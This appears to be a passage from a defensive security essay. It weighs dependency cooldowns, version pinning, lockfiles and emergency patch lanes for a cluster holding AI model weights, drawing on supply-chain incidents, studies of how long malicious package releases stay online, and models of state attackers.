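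The same policy also blocks genuine security fixes. In July 2023 a maintainer of semver, a JavaScript package with about a billion downloads a week, backported a fix to an older series and published it by hand as version 6.3.1. pnpm blocks that version as a possible takeover. When Santos-Grueiro tried to install the 1,000 most popular npm packages with the policy on, 16 failed, and semver 6.3.1 caused 14 of the failures. None of the variants he tested could distinguish a recent backport from an attack. Pinned clusters need their fast lane to deliver urgent fixes for old versions, so somebody has to read the code to check that each fix is genuine.

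A release with all the usual evidence can still be malicious. Santos-Grueiro found 119 malicious versions of 46 packages that attackers had published through the projects' own trusted pipelines. In November 2026, attackers abused the release workflows of Ethersphere, a cryptocurrency software project, to ship programs that stole wallet keys, according to The Hacker News' *Hackers Compromise Ethersphere's bee-js and Swarm Desktop to Deliver Wallet-Stealing Malware* (2026).

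### How long poisoned releases last

The essay's detection curve has a median of about 22 hours, but the 41 documented malicious releases that Santos-Grueiro studied stayed online for a median of only 3.1 hours. None with a known removal time stayed online longer than 2.5 days. A one-day cooldown would have kept out 36 of the 41, and a seven-day cooldown would have kept out 40. The removal time of the remaining release is unknown.

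*Dependency cooldowns* (Schneider, 2026), a security consultant's running account, covers most of the large campaigns since August 2025. The table adds chalk and debug, and its time for axios comes from Heffner's account.

| Campaign | What the attackers changed | Time until removal | Does a delay of a few days help? |
|---|---|---|---|
| Nx, August 2025 | New npm releases | 4 to 5 hours | Yes |
| chalk and debug, September 2025 | New npm releases | About 2 hours | Yes |
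| Trivy, March 2026 | Existing version tags on GitHub | Not given | No |
| axios, March 2026 | New npm releases | About 3 hours | Yes |
| TanStack, May 2026 | 84 new npm releases in six minutes | Hours | Yes |
| durabletask, May 2026 | New releases of a Microsoft Python package | About 2 hours | Yes |
| codfish, June 2026 | 23 existing version tags on GitHub | Not given | No |

Trivy and codfish both offer GitHub Actions, which are ready-made steps for automated builds. Developers usually refer to an action by a tag such as `v5`, and whoever controls the repository can move that tag to different code. The attackers moved old, trusted tags to malicious code instead of publishing a new version, so a rule about the age of releases wouldn't have stopped them. A build that named the exact commit by its hash would have kept using the clean code. Pinning to a commit hash and waiting therefore protect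 against different attacks, and a cluster needs both.

On 31 March 2026, a workflow that signs OpenAI's macOS apps downloaded and ran a poisoned version of axios. OpenAI's *Our response to the Axios developer tool compromise* (2026) attributes this to a configuration error in the workflow, which referred to an action by a floating tag and set no minimum age for new packages. The company found no sign that the attackers had stolen the signing certificate, but replaced it anyway.

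Six weeks later, the TanStack attack reached two OpenAI employees' devices, and the attackers stole a limited set of credentials from internal code repositories. OpenAI was already rolling out a minimum release age in response to the axios incident, but those two devices didn't have it yet, according to OpenAI's *Our response to the TanStack npm supply chain attack* (2026). The company found no evidence that its production systems or intellectual property were affected. The incidents involved office and build systems rather than a cluster that holds weights. But a single AI company ran two poisoned packages in six weeks, so a rate of one every ten years looks optimistic for organizations with many developers.

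The short times cover only attacks that somebody has found. Santos-Grueiro also included only attacks that used stolen credentials, which leaves out cases like xz, where the attacker was a maintainer. He and his colleagues cite an older study in which malicious packages stayed available for 209 days on average. A few long-lived packages can raise an average that high even if most disappear within hours.

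Some malicious packages stay available for years. *CHASE* (2026), a paper on using AI agents to analyse malicious packages, describes a PyPI package that stole Amazon cloud credentials from March 2021 until November 2024 and was downloaded 37,100 times. Arghire (2026), in *Long-Running NPM Malware Campaign Accumulates 40,000 Downloads*, describes a campaign that has published eight malicious npm packages since August 2023. A pinned cluster would not get these packages by updating software it already used, but a researcher could request one as a new dependency, and it would pass any minimum-age rule.

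Given the measured times, a cluster gets most of the protection from a delay in the first three days. After that, a longer wait helps only against poisoned releases that stay hidden for weeks. The essay puts their share at 20%, but this is the weakest guess in the model. If the true figure is 5%, extending a delay from 8 days to 30 would add only about a quarter as much protection against them.

### The dispute over cooldowns

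GitHub set Dependabot's default cooldown to three days on similar evidence. It reviewed 21 widely reported attacks from 2018 to 2026 and concluded that a cooldown could have filtered out most of them. It wanted the shortest cooldown that would outlast most attacks, and other tools already used three days. Santos-Grueiro's data supports the choice, since a three-day cooldown would have kept out the same 40 of 41 releases as a seven-day one. GitHub also says that a cooldown does little against dormant backdoors, sabotage by maintainers or a compromised build system.

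Schneider recommends waiting seven days before installing updates and says the delay has no downside. That is true only if security fixes are exempt, as he proposes. He suggests patching critical flaws within 72 hours.

Seven days is also the most common cooldown among early users. *An Exploratory Study of Dependabot Cooldown Adoption in Open-Source GitHub Projects* (Tanaka, Tsuchida and colleagues, 2026) examined 1,462 popular repositories that use Dependabot. In the ten months after the cooldown feature's release, 135 of them adopted it, and almost two thirds of the general delays they set were seven days. Many had acted on a warning from a security tool, so the figure probably reflects common advice more than anyone's calculations.

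Homebrew, a package manager for macOS and Linux, waits only one day. Schneider explains that its maintainers review every version change and apply the delay themselves. They advise against a second delay on users' machines because it would postpone urgent fixes twice. Cluster operators can easily make that mistake. If a Linux distribution has already held a package for 10 days and the cluster holds it for another 14, the total delay is 24 days.

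The software security company Sonatype rejects waiting as a strategy. Its article *Software Dependency Cooldowns Are a Symptom, Not a Strategy* argues that a package's age doesn't show that it is safe, and that a patient attacker can outlast any fixed delay. Sonatype would rather analyse each release for unusual behavior and quarantine the suspicious ones, though it accepts a short delay as a fallback. The article promotes Sonatype Firewall, the company's product for doing this, but its point about age is right. Scanners miss things too, however. Datadog, which also sells security tools, says its free scanner GuardDog can detect a malicious package only if a rule exists for the signs the attacker leaves. A delay allows time to add new rules to such tools.

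The essay behind the cost model instead proposes letting developers adopt new releases at once and hold them in staging, where the team's own tests can find faults. A high-security cluster already works this way. The essay's claim that staging allows fast adoption of security fixes is true only if staging is short, since production stays exposed until staging ends.

*Dependency cooldowns turn you into a free-rider* objects on moral grounds that people who wait are using everyone else as unpaid testers. The essay proposes that registries themselves hold each new release for a few days, while scanners examine it and maintainers get notice that it is coming. Debian already makes packages wait two to ten days before they enter its testing branch.

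The objection matters less for a single cluster than for a registry with millions of users. One more site that waits doesn't noticeably slow detection, and about 90% of the repositories that Tanaka and colleagues studied had no cooldown. Automated scanners also find many attacks without needing a victim, as happened with axios. Cluster operators can still contribute to detection by scanning the releases they hold in quarantine and reporting what they find.

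### The npm study that calls pinning futile

The strongest research finding against pinning comes from npm. He and colleagues took 10,000 npm packages and 10,000 GitHub projects and recreated the dependencies that each would have had in September 2022, and then at four later dates up to September 2023. For every project they also simulated a second version, in which the developers had pinned all their direct dependencies. They compared the two versions on five measures, three of which bear on security:

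| Average per project | Original version rules | All direct dependencies pinned |
|---|---|---|
| Dependencies with known flaws | 2.13 | 2.70 |
| Outdated direct dependencies | 5.96 | 8.78 |
| Dependency links that still accept new releases automatically | 432 | 428 |

Pinning raised the number of flawed dependencies by 27% but removed only 1% of the routes by which a poisoned update could arrive. A typical GitHub project in the sample had 11 direct dependencies and 150 indirect ones, and developers can't pin the indirect ones this way. In projects with more than 498 dependencies, pinning even increased the number of routes. About a quarter of the GitHub projects were that large.

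The increase comes from how npm handles conflicts. Suppose a project and its web framework use the same date library. If both accept a range of versions, npm can install one copy that suits them. If the project pins version 2.1.0 and the framework needs 2.3 or later, npm installs two copies, and each can bring in further dependencies that accept new releases automatically. Most other package managers allow only one version of each package, so such a pin causes an error.

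Despite its title, the study provides little evidence against running a pinned cluster. He and colleagues tested only pins on direct dependencies and assumed that nobody changed them for a year. They recommend that application developers freeze the whole dependency tree with a lockfile, as a high-security cluster does. In their sample, 44% of the GitHub projects kept a lockfile. They also counted possible attack routes and treated them all as equally likely, so the study doesn't measure how often pinned projects are compromised.

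A second simulation in the paper supports pinning the whole tree. In it, attackers pick one of the 1,000 most influential npm packages, while the maintainers of 100 well-chosen packages review every update to their dependencies and catch every malicious one. With ordinary pins, this review reduced the average spread of an attack by 30%. The reduction was 76% if the maintainers could also pass their complete lockfiles on to their users. Perfect review is a generous assumption, but it applies equally to both figures.

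### State attackers

Attacks by state-backed hackers are sometimes detected quickly. The axios attack was detected within minutes, and The Hacker News (2026) reported that Google attributed it to a North Korean group it calls UNC1069. In August 2026, *Amazon warns AI is giving North Korean hackers a dangerous advantage* (Udinmwen, 2026) reported that Amazon had linked the wider surge in poisoned open-source packages to North Korean hackers, and that generative AI was helping them disguise their code. Delaying updates by a few days works against such campaigns for now, but better disguises could make them take longer to detect.

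The model fits less well for a state agency that wants one particular set of weights, first because the agency may have zero-days. *Original Sin of npm* (2026) found that half of the flaws in npm packages took about 71 months or longer to become public after the first vulnerable version came out. An agency that discovered such a flaw at the start would have known about it for almost six years before disclosure. Installing the fix 30 days after disclosure instead of immediately would extend the time the agency could use the flaw by about 1.4%.

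Patching known flaws quickly is still worthwhile against such an agency, because on any given day the agency may not have a working zero-day for this cluster. It also risks losing a zero-day each time it uses one, whereas it loses nothing by using a public flaw. But on days when the agency has another way in, patching a known flaw does not keep it out. If it has another way in on half of all days, the emergency lane in the example saves 22.4 useful flaw-days a year instead of 44.8.

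If an agency's poisoned releases stay hidden for a year on average, 99% are still undetected after 2 days and 92% after 30. Neither lane offers much protection, so the agency gains little by targeting the fast one. The table shows how this changes the case for having an emergency lane. Its inputs are again invented, and it assumes that the attacker always targets the emergency lane.

| Attacker | Dangerous flaw-days the lane saves each year | Extra compromises it causes | The lane pays if the daily chance of theft exceeds |
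|---|---|---|---|
| Uses only known flaws, follows the essay's detection curve | 44.8 | One in 42 years | 1 in 1,900 |
| The same, but has a zero-day half the time | 22.4 | One in 42 years | 1 in 950 |
| Has a zero-day half the time and hides code for a year on average | 22.4 | One in 136 years | 1 in 3,050 |

The emergency lane is easier to justify in the last row than in the first, because waiting would not stop that attacker's code. The figures also show that neither kind of delay does much against such an attacker. *Securing AI Model Weights* (Nevo, Lahav and colleagues, 2024), the RAND report that defined the five security levels, judged that nobody could yet protect a model that interacts with the internet from the most capable attackers. The measures it recommended starting early included completely isolated networks and physical limits on how fast data can leave. Both work whether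 the attacker came in through an old flaw, a new one or a poisoned update.

Adding up flaw-days, as the model does, is also misleading here because it counts thirty flaws that each last one day the same as one flaw that lasts thirty days. The long-lived flaw is far more useful to a patient attacker who already has an account inside the cluster. Suppose the attacker needs five days to build a reliable exploit after a flaw becomes public. A 30-day delay leaves both dangerous flaws each year open long enough to exploit, while the 2-day lane leaves only those that triage misses, one every two and a half years.

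Against that attacker, shortening the lane from two days to one wouldn't help. But if AI tools cut the five days to a few hours, every dangerous flaw would stay open long enough to be exploited, even with the lane. The operators would then have to rely on compensating controls they can switch on within an hour or two of disclosure, and on nodes where a stolen account can't reach the weights.
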